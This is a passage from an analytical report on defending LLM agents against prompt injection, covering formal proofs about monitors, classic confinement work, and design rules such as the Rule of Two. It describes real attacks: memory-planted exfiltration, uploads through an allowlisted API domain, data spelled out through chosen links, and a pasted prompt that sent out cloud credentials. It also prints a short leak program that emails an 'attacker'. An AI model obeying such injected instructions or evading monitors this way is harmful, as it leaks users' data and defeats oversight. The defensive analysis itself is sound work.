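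The fence also prevents the plan from using the tool. In Dongol's model of a reported attack on GitHub, for example, Alice asks an agent to look at the open issues in her public code repository. One issue contains an instruction to publish data from her private repositories in a pull request, a proposed change that everyone can read. A fence on pull requests stops the attack, but it would also stop the agent from proposing a fix if Alice wanted it to fix the issues.

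Relative security doesn't reflect this loss, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and loses the same tool. A monitor that denies every call therefore also satisfies relative security. Operators have to test separately whether the agent still completes its tasks.

An agent that works through an inbox all day needs its tools back for each new email. If a new message from Alice restores them while the previous email is still in the model's context, the model can obey an instruction in the previous email and leak data from Alice's. Dongol therefore proves a second theorem for a session fence, which restores tools only when the model starts a new session with an empty context. Such an agent may run forever, so the theorem also requires that the model cannot obey injected instructions forever without returning to the plan.

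A new session is fresh only if it carries over nothing from the attacker. In the SpAIware attack of 2024, a web page made ChatGPT save an instruction in its long-term memory, which the service loaded into every later conversation. Each answer then displayed an image whose address contained the user's messages. In Dongol's model of the attack, restoring the tools at each new session fails because the stored instruction comes back with the memory. The session fence works again if the monitor treats the memory as untrusted and withdraws the tools when it is loaded.

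The theorem also fails if an injected instruction can start a program that changes the plan's memory. Suppose the plan sends a stranger's email back to him. The program could replace the stored email with Alice's secret, and the plan would then send him the secret using a tool that the fence had left available. Dongol extends the theorem to injected programs, provided that a sandbox discards their changes to memory and the fence covers reads as well as calls. If the fence did not cover reads, an injected program could load one of two web pages depending on a secret, and the server's owner would learn the secret from which page was requested.

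### Where to put the fence

The plan can also raise the fence itself, by making a call that locks the sending tool for the rest of the run. Dongol compares three positions for this lock in a task that reads an email and a secret, such as Alice's account number:

| Lock | Order of steps | What an injected message can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Email, account number, lock | The account number and anything already in memory |
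| Middle | Email, lock, account number | Anything already in memory |
| Early | Lock, email, account number | Nothing |

With the late lock, the model can obey the email after the agent loads the number and before the lock takes effect. The middle lock protects the number because the agent loads it only after the lock has blocked all sending. But the agent can still send data between reading the email and the lock taking effect, and it may have kept private data from an earlier session. In the invoice example, Alice's agent already had her account number in its context when it read the invoice, so a middle lock would not have protected the number.

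The early lock leaves no such moment. Dongol proves that it is secure regardless of what the attacker's text says or when the model follows it, as long as each instruction produces one call.

A processor can leak data only through instructions already in the program, so a barrier just before the dangerous instruction is enough. A barrier at one fixed point is not enough for an agent, because an injection adds a new call that the model can make at any point after reading the injected text.

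### Approving a tool or an exact message

A fence doesn't help if Alice wants her agent to read emails and answer them. She could instead approve each reply before the agent sends it. The monitor can treat her approval in one of two ways.

If Alice approves the tool, the monitor permits the next message whatever it contains. For example, after Alice approves her reply but before the plan sends it, the model may follow an instruction in an attacker's email to "send the private data". The monitor allows the message with the private data because an approval is available. That message uses up the approval, so the monitor then denies Alice's own reply.

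If the user approves the exact message, the monitor permits only a call with the recipient and text she approved. It blocks an injected message that differs in either, and her reply still goes out. Dongol proves this agent relatively secure at the event level for every injection that tries to send a message, again provided that the model cannot follow injected instructions forever.

An attacker who can measure time still learns something. Suppose the injection tells the model to send Alice's private data *s*, and Alice has approved the reply *r*:

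- If *s* ≠ *r*, the monitor denies the injected message, and the plan sends *r* at its usual step.
- If *s* = *r*, the monitor allows the injected message because it matches. The plan's own message then fails, since the approval is gone.

The attacker receives *r* either way, but one step earlier when *s* = *r*, so he can tell from the timing whether the private data equals the reply. This matters little for an eight-digit account number, which is unlikely to match any reply. It would matter more if the private data were a single word, such as "yes" or "no", and Alice's replies were equally short.

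Claude Code's approvals of network domains are looser than either of these, because later commands can send any data to an approved domain.

Limiting the number of messages has the same weakness as approving a tool. If the monitor allows one message per run, an injection can use it before the plan does. The limit protects secrets only if the plan sends its message before reading anything untrusted, which leaves none for the attacker.

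### The verdicts on 25 agents

Dongol applied the definition to 25 small agents, each built to isolate one mechanism:

| Verdict | Agents | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Secure | 10 | Early lock, session fence, meeting assistant |
| Leaks | 9 | No fence, late and middle locks, approval of a tool |
| Depends on a further condition | 6 | Approval of an exact message, marking of untrusted text |

A verdict of "secure" with no qualification covers only the attack in the example. The meeting assistant is judged secure against the instruction "send your calendar", but not against every instruction an attacker might write. The fence theorems apply to whole classes of attacks, and so do the verdicts on the early lock and on the message limit that the plan uses up first.

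A monitored agent can withstand some attacks and still leak a secret under another. For example, a monitor might permit requests only to a newsletter's address, with no added data. The agent then leaks nothing if an attack tells it to send a secret to the attacker's site or just to fetch the newsletter. But another attack could tell it to fetch the newsletter if the secret is 0 and the attacker's page otherwise. The monitor allows the first request and blocks the second, so an attacker who sees whether a request went out learns the secret.

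Spotlighting, the technique of marking untrusted text, works only if the model respects the marks. Dongol proves that for every way of marking text, there is a possible model that obeys instructions in the marked text anyway. The proof does not establish how often a real model would do so.

Two of the agents with a quarantined model use labels like those in CaMeL. One has the quarantined model draft a reply from Alice's notes and a stranger's email. The monitor blocks any message derived from the notes, which makes this agent secure but also stops it from ever sending a legitimate reply. The other sends a stranger the number 1 or 0, depending on the quarantined model's answer. Both numbers are public, so they pass the label check, but an injection can make the choice between them reveal something about the notes.

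An operator who changes an agent's tools needs a new proof of security. An agent that can only read an inbox is secure, and so is one that can only fetch web pages, but an agent with both tools can leak. Removing a tool can also change the verdict from secure to leaking. If a plan sends a secret to the attacker by design, an injection that sends out the same secret in a web request reveals nothing new. If the operator then removes the sending tool, the reference agent no longer reveals the secret, so the web request counts as a leak, even though the agent as a whole reveals no more than before.

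Dongol did the work in Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks every step of a mathematical proof. The proofs take up about 31,600 lines in 89 files. Claude Code helped generate the theorems and proofs, and Dongol compared each definition and theorem in the paper with its Isabelle version. An error in the logic is therefore unlikely. It is more likely that the mathematical model of an agent differs from a real agent, because Isabelle cannot check for that.

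### What a real system must provide

For the theorems to apply to a real agent, its program has to satisfy seven assumptions:

| Assumption | What it requires | Example of a failure |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted execution | A trusted program runs the plan, so the model cannot skip or change steps | The model itself redirects a planned email |
| Complete mediation | No tool call or read of untrusted text can bypass the monitor, and the monitor handles requests one by one | The agent runs a browser that the monitor does not control |
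| Mediated reads | Untrusted text enters the context only after the monitor has allowed the read | The program loads a page before asking the monitor |
| Silent denials | A refused request has no effect that the attacker can see | A public log lists refusals |
| Limited observation | The attacker sees neither the monitor's state nor the agent's internal steps | Displaying an answer loads an image from the attacker's server |
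| Fresh sessions | A new session clears everything the model kept from untrusted text | Long-term memory carries an instruction over |
| Trusted channels | The attacker cannot write to any source the agent treats as trusted | A calendar accepts invitations from outsiders |

If an attacker can see refusals, the theorem for silent denials does not apply, and the operator needs a proof that covers such an attacker. These proofs do not examine the code of real monitors, so they do not show whether those monitors meet the other assumptions.

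The theorems do not cover some agents, even if their monitors work perfectly. The largest excluded group is agents whose model chooses every call as it goes. These agents have no plan before the first untrusted read, so there is no reference agent to compare them with.

The theorems also exclude tools whose reply depends on the request. An attacker who runs a search engine, for example, sees Alice's query, which may contain private data, and can tailor the answer to it. The theorems do not cover side channels, systems of several agents, or mistakes by the planner either. Relative security covers only leaks, so an injection that makes the agent delete a file without revealing anything does not violate it.

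Dongol does not say how many deployed agents these exclusions leave out. The closest evidence comes from *Measuring Agents in Production* (2025), which covered 306 practitioners and 20 detailed case studies, according to *The Hierarchy of Agentic Capabilities* (2026). Workflows with steps defined in advance dominated the case studies. In the survey, 68% of deployed agents ran fewer than ten steps before a person had to intervene, and 47% fewer than five.

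These figures don't settle the question. A company can define a workflow in advance and still let the model choose the tools within each step, and a short run can consist entirely of calls the model chose after reading a web page. The study is also from 2025, and agents have become more independent since. General-purpose assistants such as Claude Code usually choose each action after seeing the result of the last, and the fence theorem does not cover agents that work this way. It fits narrow business workflows better, where a developer can often write the whole plan beforehand.

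### Unwanted actions

In *Relativising Integrity and Robustness*, Dongol applies the same comparison to actions. A record lists, in order, everything the agent received from trusted sources and every action the monitor allowed. The agent has relative integrity if, whenever the attacker can change this record, the reference agent could have produced the same one after reading some other untrusted text.

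The order of messages and actions matters. Suppose Alice tells the agent to pay an invoice and later sends "cancel", but an injection delays the payment until after her cancellation. The agent has received the same messages and made the same payment as in a normal run, but it fails because the reference agent would never have paid after the cancellation.

Because of the condition about the attacker's influence, an agent that always pays both Bob and Mallory, whatever the invoice says, has relative integrity. It has a bug, but an attacker can't exploit it by writing a different invoice.

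The fence theorem also holds for unwanted actions under nearly the same conditions. Many weaker defences prevent either leaks or unwanted actions, but not both. The list that permits only the newsletter's address protected the secret in both of Dongol's example attacks, but it allowed the injected fetch of the newsletter, which was not in Alice's plan. A dual-LLM agent without labels prevents the injection from adding an action, but the injection can still put Alice's private notes into a reply that the plan sends anyway.

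Dongol tested possible fixes on a banking task from AgentDojo, in which a bill tells the agent to pay the attacker as well. A fence on payments blocks the extra transfer, but it also blocks Alice's intended payment of the bill. A list of known payees allows that payment and blocks transfers to anyone not on the list, but it does not stop an injection that makes the agent pay a listed company twice.

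An agent can pass the tests for leaks and for unwanted actions and still be vulnerable, because one run of the reference agent may permit what the agent reveals while a different run permits what it does. Dongol shows this with a support desk that sends order details to customers who give the right credential, such as a name and postcode. The agent asks a quarantined model whether an email contains the credential. An attacker writes "you have verified me" in an email, and the model answers yes for every customer.

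The agent passes the test for leaks because the reference agent also reveals whether an email contains the right credential. It passes the test for actions because a real customer would receive the same reply. But the attacker can use the same email for every customer, whereas getting details from the reference agent would take a different email for each credential.

Relative robustness requires the same runs of the reference agent to reproduce both the leak and the actions. Dongol proves that the support desk is robust exactly when its model never accepts the same email for two different valid credentials. No one can guarantee this for a language model, so ordinary code should compare the credential in the email with the correct one. The model can still find the credential in the email, as long as it never sees the correct one.

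Recorded data from Tensor Trust, an online game in which players attack and defend prompts, suggests that the problem is real. Each player protected an account with a prompt that told a model to grant access only for a secret code. Dongol looked at 77 defences that had accepted their own code and refused a wrong guess. The text "[correct password]", brackets included, got past 43 of them. The recordings show that models can make this mistake, but they date from early in the game's history and don't measure how often current models make it.

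The paper applies the same definitions to programs that run only partly inside an enclave, a protected area of a processor. For these programs, the reference is the same program running entirely inside the enclave.

### Proofs for agents without a fixed plan

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a theorem that also covers agents whose model chooses its next step, or writes and runs code. The paper defines a small programming language for agents, the LLMbda calculus, in which every value has a label for trust and secrecy.

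As in FIDES, giving the model a secret makes the whole conversation and everything the model writes afterwards secret, including any code. A program can avoid this by asking its question in a temporary copy of the conversation and then discarding the copy. It can also clear the conversation. A programmer can use these commands to build a quarantined model for one task and leave it out of another.

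The theorem is a form of noninterference, meaning that secrets don't affect what an observer limited to public data sees. Because a language model chooses its words partly at random, the theorem compares the probabilities of what the observer sees in two runs that start with different secrets. The one exception is that a secret may affect whether the program finishes. A run that the monitor stops for breaking a policy counts as unfinished.

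This exception has a limit. If μ and ν are the probabilities of the observable results in the two cases, and div is the probability that a run does not finish, then

Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2

where Δ is the statistical distance. To calculate it, one takes the difference between the two probabilities of each observable result, ignoring the sign, adds up these differences and halves the sum. If 2% of runs fail to finish with one secret and 4% with the other, the distance is at most 3%.

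Garby and colleagues motivate their work with leaks in CaMeL, which already tracks some of the conditions under which an action takes place. The following program, adapted from their example, tells an attacker whether Alice's balance is above £5,000:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 5000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker", "rich")
```

If Alice has £8,000, the third line sets `tmp` to False and labels it secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` stays True and keeps its public label. The last line therefore appears to depend only on public data, and CaMeL allows the email. If Alice has £3,000, the fourth line sets `rich` to False and no email goes out.

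An injection cannot easily produce this program, because CaMeL's planner would have to write it and the planner never reads the attacker's text. The example still disproves the assumption that the labels catch every flow. A second leak comes from the ordinary program around CaMeL, which retries after a failure. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can reveal one yes/no answer about a secret, so an attacker can use the retries to collect the whole secret. The LLMbda calculus prevents the first kind of leak by stopping a program that tries to change a public conversation when the change depends on a secret condition.

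Garby and colleagues checked their theorems in Lean, another proof assistant. Their proof includes the program that calls the model, which leaves less room for a mismatch between the mathematics and the code than in Dongol's work. They also tested an agent written in the calculus on AgentDojo's banking tasks. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks off, and turning those checks on halved the number CaMeL completed. Attacks on the new agent succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. The theorem covers how labels spread, so the result still depends on the programmer labelling the data correctly and writing the right policies.

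Programmers also have to write exceptions. The calculus has a command that marks untrusted data as trusted, and Garby and colleagues prove that using it does not weaken the protection of secrets. The meeting assistant needs an exception for secrets instead, because it is meant to send private data to strangers. In Dongol's approach, that exception follows from the plan, but the agent must have a plan before it reads the first email.

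## What an injected instruction can still do with permitted actions

Even if Alice's monitor applies its policy without a mistake and nothing escapes from her secondary VM, the hidden line in her invoice can still do harm by making the agent misuse actions that the policy permits. Alice can't forbid all of these actions, because the agent needs them for its work. Computer scientists faced this problem decades before LLM agents existed, first with programs that had to handle data without leaking it, and then with a program that used its authority for the wrong person.

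### The confused deputy

Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that rented out time on its computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the computer can run, recorded statistics in a file in its own directory. To allow this, the operating system let the compiler write to any file in that directory, including the company's billing records. Users could also name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one of them named the billing file. The operating system checked whether the compiler had permission to write to that file and found that it did, so the debugging output replaced the billing records.

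The check applied the rules correctly. But the compiler had authority from both the company that installed it and the user who ran it, and it had no way to specify which authority it was using. Tymshare added a command for choosing between them, but some programs soon needed more than two authorities. Checking file names would not have helped much either, because someone would have had to update the compiler whenever the directory gained another sensitive file.

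Hardy recommends capabilities instead. A capability identifies a file and carries the right to use it. The user would have passed the compiler a capability for the output file rather than a file name. A user without access to the billing file would have had no capability for that file to pass on.

Alice's agent has the same defect as the compiler, because an ordinary tool call does not identify whose wishes the agent is carrying out. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) similarly warns companies that a valid credential may let an agent into a system without establishing which actions somebody has authorised. Alice could apply Hardy's remedy by replacing the agent's general right to make payments with a right to pay one supplier, at the account number in her own records. A different account number in the invoice would then have no effect.

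### The confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) asks how a customer can use someone else's program without letting it send the customer's data to its owner. Lampson assumes the system already blocks all unauthorised access. Even then, the program can harm the customer by doing its job badly or by leaking the data it received for the job. Lampson knew of no general technical remedy for bad work except certifying the program, though he pointed out that the customer at least has the wrong output as evidence. A leak usually leaves no sign. In the invoice example, Alice is the customer, and the attacker who wrote the hidden line takes the place of the program's owner.

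Lampson divides the possible routes for a leak into three kinds:

| Channel | Lampson's example | A similar route for Alice's agent |
|---|---|---|
| Storage | The program writes to a file that its owner reads later | A summary in a folder that other people can read |
| Legitimate | The program encodes data in the bill that its owner receives | The amount or reference text of a payment |
| Covert, meaning not intended to carry information at all | The program varies its use of the processor, and another program measures the effect | The moment at which a permitted payment arrives |

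An injected instruction can leak private data through even a small permitted channel. For example, if the agent can choose the pence in each payment, it can send two digits at a time, so four payments would reveal an eight-digit account number to the recipient.

The simplest solution is total isolation, in which the confined program may not call any other program. Lampson considers this impractical, because even harmless-looking requests to the operating system can leak data. For example, some systems do not let one program write to a file while another is reading it. A confined program with read-only access can then open the file or leave it closed, and an outside program can tell whether it is open by trying to write to it. Repeating this can transfer a secret one bit at a time.

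Lampson's alternative is masking, in which the customer determines everything the program puts into its legitimate and covert channels. For the bill, the customer calculates the price beforehand from a published description, and the program may refuse the job. For covert channels, the operating system has to make the program's visible behavior match what the customer specified, for instance by slowing the program down or adding pointless disk accesses. A customer who can accept a small leak could instead have the system limit how much data these channels carry.

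Covert channels have remained the hardest to close. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Lipner concluded in a 1975 reply that a system could close storage and legitimate channels with little sacrifice, but that closing covert channels seemed to require an unreasonable loss of performance.

An operator should still deal with the larger channels first. Willison's collected attacks on agents send data through web requests, images and file uploads, which carry far more data than variations in timing. An attacker has little reason to use a covert channel while one of these is open.

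### A wrong figure or a different payee

If the hidden line makes the agent report the wrong amount, Alice has the evidence that Lampson mentions, because she can compare the summary with the invoice. But she asked for a summary to avoid reading the invoice, so she may notice the error only when the supplier complains.

The harm is greater if the agent can also make payments. *An Introduction to Google's Approach to AI Agent Security* (Willison, 2025) quotes an example policy from Google that blocks purchases above $500 and asks the user about those between $100 and $500. Under this policy, the agent could pay $90 to the wrong account without asking. The limit reduces the loss from one payment, but the operator also has to limit the total, because an attacker could use many small payments.

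Masking works better for some payments. Lampson compares it to purchase orders, in which the buyer sets the price before the seller sends a bill. Alice's program could take the payee from her list of suppliers and the amount from her order, and pay only if the invoice matches both. The attacker could then stop a payment by writing a wrong figure, but could not redirect or increase it. If the program also marks each order as paid, a second copy of the invoice cannot trigger another payment.

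This works only when Alice has a record from another source. A new supplier is not on her list, and she does not know the amount of an electricity bill in advance. For a summary, there is usually no second record to check against. Typed results limit the form an answer can take, but an answer in the correct form can still be false.

### Data sent to a permitted address

Claude Cowork originally allowed network connections only to a list of domains. The list had to include Anthropic's API, which programs use to access Claude, because Cowork cannot work without it. In January 2026, the security firm PromptArmor showed how to steal files through this domain, as Willison reported at the time.

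The attack began with a malicious file in the user's folder that contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload other files from the folder to that account. The virtual machine worked correctly, but the network proxy let the upload through because it checked only the destination, which was on the allowlist.

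Anthropic added a proxy inside the virtual machine that passes a request to the API only if it carries the token issued for that session, so requests with the attacker's key are rejected. The proxy also blocks request headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch data from elsewhere. Anthropic placed the proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers cannot distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's request. But code with full control of the virtual machine might be able to bypass the proxy.

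Anthropic concluded that an entry on such a list grants the agent every function available at that address. Several other products had similar gaps. According to Willison, the default list in Google's programming tool Antigravity included a public service where anyone can set up a page and read the requests sent to it. Salesforce's list of trusted image sources included an expired domain, so researchers were able to register it and receive customer data. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without approval, and images in those emails could send data out when the user opened the message.

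A stricter rule about addresses also failed in Claude's chat service. Its web tool could open only addresses that the user had typed, a search had returned, or a page it had already opened linked to. The model therefore could not put a secret into a new address. The researcher Ayush Paul built a site with a link for each letter and persuaded the model to spell out information about its user by choosing one link after another. The order of its choices revealed the user's name, home city and employer, even though none of the addresses contained a secret when the model received it. With 26 links on a page, each choice can carry up to 4.7 bits. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links found on pages it has opened.

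A monitor can close some of these gaps by checking what a request does as well as where it goes. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes this for the web version of Claude Code, which works on code in the user's GitHub account. The sandbox contains only a limited credential. When Claude uploads a change, a proxy outside the sandbox checks that the change goes to the permitted branch (a separate line of development) and then attaches the real credential, so the agent cannot use the real credential for anything else. The agent can still include a secret in the uploaded code, so access to the branch must be limited to people who are allowed to have the secret.

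### A file that takes effect later

Lampson requires that a confined program keep nothing from one call to the next. Most agents do not meet this requirement, because people want them to remember earlier work.

Suppose the hidden line in Alice's March invoice makes the agent write in its summary that the supplier has moved to an account at a different bank. The policy permits the agent to save the summary, and the added sentence contains no secret. In April, Alice asks the agent to pay the supplier, and the agent looks up the account in its old summaries. The March invoice is no longer in the agent's context, so if the monitor counts the agent's own files as trusted, a fence does not take effect.

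The sample file policy happens to prevent this, because the agent may write summaries but not read them. If Alice adds read access so that the agent can compare each month with the previous one, an instruction hidden in the March invoice could affect the April payment through the March summary.

The SpAIware attack used ChatGPT's memory in much the same way, and Anthropic expects such attacks to become a larger problem as agents keep more material between sessions. Anthropic also warns that in systems with several agents, the main agent may trust a helper's report more than a raw web page, even though the helper wrote the report after reading that page. The monitor has to keep treating such reports, like text saved in memory, as untrusted.

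Some files take effect without any model reading them. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let a project run code in Claude Code before the user had agreed to trust the project. In the simplest case, a developer downloaded a project to review it, and its settings file contained an attacker's hook, a command that runs automatically. Claude Code read the settings and ran the hook at startup, before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. Anthropic now delays reading these settings until the user has agreed.

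That attack needed no injection, but an agent that can write such a file could prepare the same attack for a later session. Claude Code's sandbox protects its own settings files for this reason. Protecting a fixed list of files doesn't cover the ordinary files an agent produces in its work. A programmer who asks an agent to fix a script will probably run it afterwards, possibly outside the sandbox. The attacker loses this advantage if the programmer runs the script under the same restrictions or checks the changes first.

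### A user who approves the attack

When a policy neither allows nor forbids a request, many products ask the user. Anthropic reported in May 2026 that users of Claude Code approved about 93% of its permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the figure at 97% in August. Most of the requests were probably harmless, so these rates alone do not prove that people are careless.

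Anthropic also had a research vendor run an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. During each session, the vendor replaced the text of one approval prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic calls this decline approval fatigue. A separate model that reviewed the same commands blocked 89% of them.

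The experiment has limits. Anthropic published it to support replacing most prompts with that model. The testers worked in an artificial environment where mistakes could not damage their own files, so they may have been less careful than at home. But this does not easily explain the decline over a session, since the environment was artificial from the start.

People seem to pay more attention when asked to approve something larger. Users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude Code presented, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Some of the rejected plans were probably unsuitable rather than dangerous, so the difference is only weak evidence that people are better at judging the security of plans than of individual requests. Many users avoid the prompts entirely, and a quarter of interactive sessions start with permission checks turned off.

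In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing cut the number of permission prompts by 84%, though this figure doesn't measure how many attacks the sandbox stopped. Fewer prompts should reduce fatigue, but the testers missed most dangerous commands even at the start. The greater benefit is that the sandbox enforces its limits on the actions that no longer trigger a prompt, without relying on anyone's attention.

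An attentive user may also lack the knowledge to decide. If the agent asks Alice to approve a £900 payment to a new account, she can't tell whether the supplier changed banks, even if the prompt is accurate. Anthropic therefore argues that the strength of the isolation should depend on what users can judge. It asks programmers for approval because they can usually read a shell command, but it gave Cowork a fixed boundary because office workers often can't read shell commands.

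Attackers can also persuade the user to give the agent malicious instructions. In an internal test in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher sent an employee an email that looked like a normal request from a colleague and included a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Among its routine steps, the prompt told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Anthropic ran the prompt 25 times, and the credentials left the machine in 24 of those runs.

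The instruction came from the user, not a document, so a fence that activates only when untrusted content appears would not have taken effect. A model that checks whether an action matches the user's wishes would not have found anything unusual either. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the environment work here. Egress control can block the upload regardless of who asked for it, and file restrictions can keep Claude from accessing the credentials.

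After the test, employees shared the working prompt in Anthropic's internal chat to discuss it, until someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read that chat. They then added a distinctive piece of text to the discussion so they would notice if an agent picked it up.

### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

A policy that permits an action usually permits it whether Alice or an instruction in the invoice caused it. Two simple rules avoid this problem by restricting which abilities one agent may combine.

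*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) advises users never to combine private data, untrusted content and outside communication, the three things that together exposed Alice's account number. The advice is mainly for people who connect tools from different makers, because a tool that is safe alone may become unsafe when they add another. A tool that reads email already provides both private data and untrusted content, since an inbox contains private messages and anyone can write to it.

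Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this idea into a design rule. Until models can reliably detect and refuse injections, an agent should have at most two of these properties in one session:

- **A:** It processes untrusted input.
- **B:** It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It can change something or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three, the agent must not work on its own. A person has to approve its actions, or the operator needs another reliable way to check them.

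Meta's rule covers more than data theft. Suppose an agent can read and pay invoices but has no access to private data. It satisfies Willison's rule, yet a false invoice could still make it pay an attacker. Under Meta's rule, the payment system counts as sensitive and making a payment changes state, so the agent has all three properties and needs supervision.

Meta gives three examples of agents that each give up one property:

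| Agent | What it keeps | How it limits the third property |
|---|---|---|
| Travel assistant | Web content and the user's private data | A person confirms bookings and payments, and the agent does not visit addresses it has constructed itself |
| Research assistant | Web content and free use of websites | The browser has no saved logins, and the agent has little private data |
| Internal programming agent | Access to company systems and the ability to change them | A filter admits only data from trusted authors |

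The rules protect Alice against some of the harms in this section:

| Harm | Avoiding the lethal trifecta | Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|
| False summary | Does not prevent it | Does not prevent it, as Meta acknowledges |
| Payment to the wrong account | Prevents it only if the missing ability is one the attack needs | Requires approval |
| Theft through a permitted address | Prevents it if the operator counts that address as outside communication | The same |
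| Planted file | May miss it if the agent that reads the file counts it as trusted | The same, because the limit applies to each session |
| Persuaded user | Prevents theft only if the agent has no way to send data | Approval is the exception that permits all three properties |

Either rule can be hard to apply because the operator has to classify each tool correctly. Cowork's API address looked like part of the product, but an attacker could use it to receive files. Claude's web tool did not let the model construct addresses, a rule close to Meta's for the travel assistant, but it still leaked data because the attacker had supplied the links.

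A planted file can get around the two-property limit because the limit applies only "in one session". An agent might read a web page and save a note in a session without private data, then read that note in a later session with access to Alice's bank. Each session has only two of the properties if the operator treats the note as trusted. The author filter in Meta's programming example could stop this, but only if the note still counts as the web page author's text after the agent has rewritten it.

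Meta allows an agent to change its permitted combination during a session. For example, it could first browse the web without private data, then lose its ability to communicate before it gains access to internal systems. This resembles the middle lock in Dongol's comparison, and any private data already in the agent's memory could likewise leak before the lock.

Both rules also exclude tasks that people want agents to perform alone. An email assistant that uses its user's calendar to answer strangers needs all three abilities, and so does a programming agent that reads public documentation, works on private code and uploads the result. Meta acknowledges that its rule fits background tasks badly, because nobody is there to approve actions. When someone does approve each step, the result depends on whether they pay close attention, which Anthropic's testers mostly did not.

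OpenAI offers ChatGPT users a version of this trade-off in Lockdown Mode, which restricts outgoing network requests so that an injection has fewer ways to send data out. The mode reached personal accounts in June 2026. Willison approves of it because fixed rules enforce the restriction, and because he thinks outside communication is the easiest of the three abilities to remove without making an agent much less useful. OpenAI warns that an injection can still make an answer wrong. Its head of security recommends the mode for people at higher risk and says it is not meant for everyone, since it removes some functions.

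Alice could divide the work between two sessions. The first would read the invoice in the secondary VM and return only the amount and the due date. The second would have her bank access and make the payment. This satisfies the Rule of Two only if those two values, which come from a stranger's invoice, no longer count as untrusted input. Either way, the second session should compare the amount with her order.

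## Why the monitor is hard to trust

A monitor's guarantees depend on assumptions about the monitor itself. Dongol's theorems, for example, assume that no request can bypass it. Anderson's panel turned such assumptions into three requirements: the system must invoke the monitor on every access, the monitor must be tamperproof, and it must be small enough to verify.

*Causality Laundering* argues that its monitor, ARM, meets all three of Anderson's requirements. ARM is the only proxy between the model and the tool server, runs in its own process, and has four layers of checks with fixed rules that people can test one layer at a time. These choices are sensible, but they do not fully establish what Anderson asked for. Whether ARM is the only route to the tools depends on how the operator installs it, and testing the four layers separately does not prove that the whole monitor is correct.

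### What each requirement would take

To show that the monitor checks every access, an operator would have to list every way the agent can affect something outside the model. For Alice's agent, the list includes its file tool, web tool and shell, but also any script these start, any helper agent, and any file that another program will run later. The operator could easily miss something. It is safer to block every route in the operating system or virtual machine and then open one that leads through the monitor.

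To show that nobody can tamper with the monitor, the operator needs a list of everything the monitor reads: its program, its policy, saved approvals, its log, and whatever it stores about past events. No tool may let the agent change any of these, even if the change takes effect only after a restart.

To verify a monitor, people need a precise statement of what it should do and a trusted computing base small enough to check against that statement. The kernels that today's sandboxes rely on are much larger than GCOS III, which Anderson considered too large.

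*Ring-0 by Default* applies the three requirements to published defences. Rules written in the prompt fail all three, because the model may ignore them, injected text can override them, and nobody can inspect a neural network to see how it will respond. Defences outside the model, such as hooks on tool calls, information-flow control and host sandboxes, meet the requirements on bypassing and tampering. The study also counts host sandboxes as verifiable, but only in the sense that someone can check the policy in advance. Anderson required the mechanism itself to be checkable, and a sandbox on an ordinary kernel doesn't meet that standard.

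### Agents compared with operating systems

Like an operating system, an agent now starts processes, manages files, contacts other computers, loads extensions and saves its state. *Ring-0 by Default* examines how many of an operating system's protections agents also have. It argues that agents in effect run in ring 0, the processor mode in which a kernel has full privileges, because whatever the model writes runs with the user's full authority.

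The researchers took 116 mechanisms from standard textbooks and looked for the counterpart of each in agents' documentation, source code and the research literature:

| Verdict | Meaning | Mechanisms |
|---|---|---|
| Equivalent | Works essentially as in an operating system | 11 |
| Degraded | Exists, but its protection fails if the model disobeys or the agent takes a route that the check does not cover | 26 |
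| Missing | The researchers found no counterpart | 65 |
| Mutated | Exists but behaves differently, for example because the agent can rewrite it | 14 |

Nine of the 116 also count as novel, meaning they raise a problem operating systems do not have. Tokens are an example, since an agent that uses too many wastes money as well as computing time. Of the 11 equivalent mechanisms, only four are protections, and all four work at the boundary between the agent and its host. The missing mechanisms include resource limits, signatures for extensions, and transactions, which let a system undo a half-completed change.

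The 65 missing mechanisms do not amount to 65 vulnerabilities, because the study examines only the agent itself and ignores any external sandbox. If Alice's operator runs her agent in a container with a memory limit, the study still counts the agent as lacking one, even though the container protects the host.

The researchers tested 25 of the mechanisms in thirteen experiments on Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, three command-line programming agents. Each run used a fresh container with no internet access. In some runs, a script issued the tool calls in place of the model, to test whether the program around the model would block an action regardless of what the model decided. In others, a real model made the decisions, usually five times for each case. "Bypass mode" in the table is a setting that stops the agent from asking for permission.

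| What the experiment tested | Result |
|---|---|
| Writing outside the project folder | One agent's file tool refused even in bypass mode, but a shell command worked in all three |
| Contacting an internal server | The built-in web tools of two agents checked the destination, but shell commands reached it in all three |
| Changing the agent's own settings | All three could do so in bypass mode, and one also in a stricter mode |
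| Using a model as the monitor | Both monitors tested blocked the action whenever the model failed to give a valid answer |
| Keeping notes | All three loaded their own notes as instructions in later sessions |
| Permissions after resuming a session | The earlier permission mode did not carry over, but in one agent a scheduled task did |
| Overwriting a file that had just changed | Only one built-in tool refused, though real models preserved the newer changes in every valid run |
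| Believing a false time | Models ignored a false date in a note but accepted a false time from a tool |
| Loading an altered session record | All three accepted a forged entry as a message from the user |
| Removing fetched pages after a task | Their text stayed in the session record |
| Isolating the reading of files | One of the two agents tested started a restricted helper process for each file |
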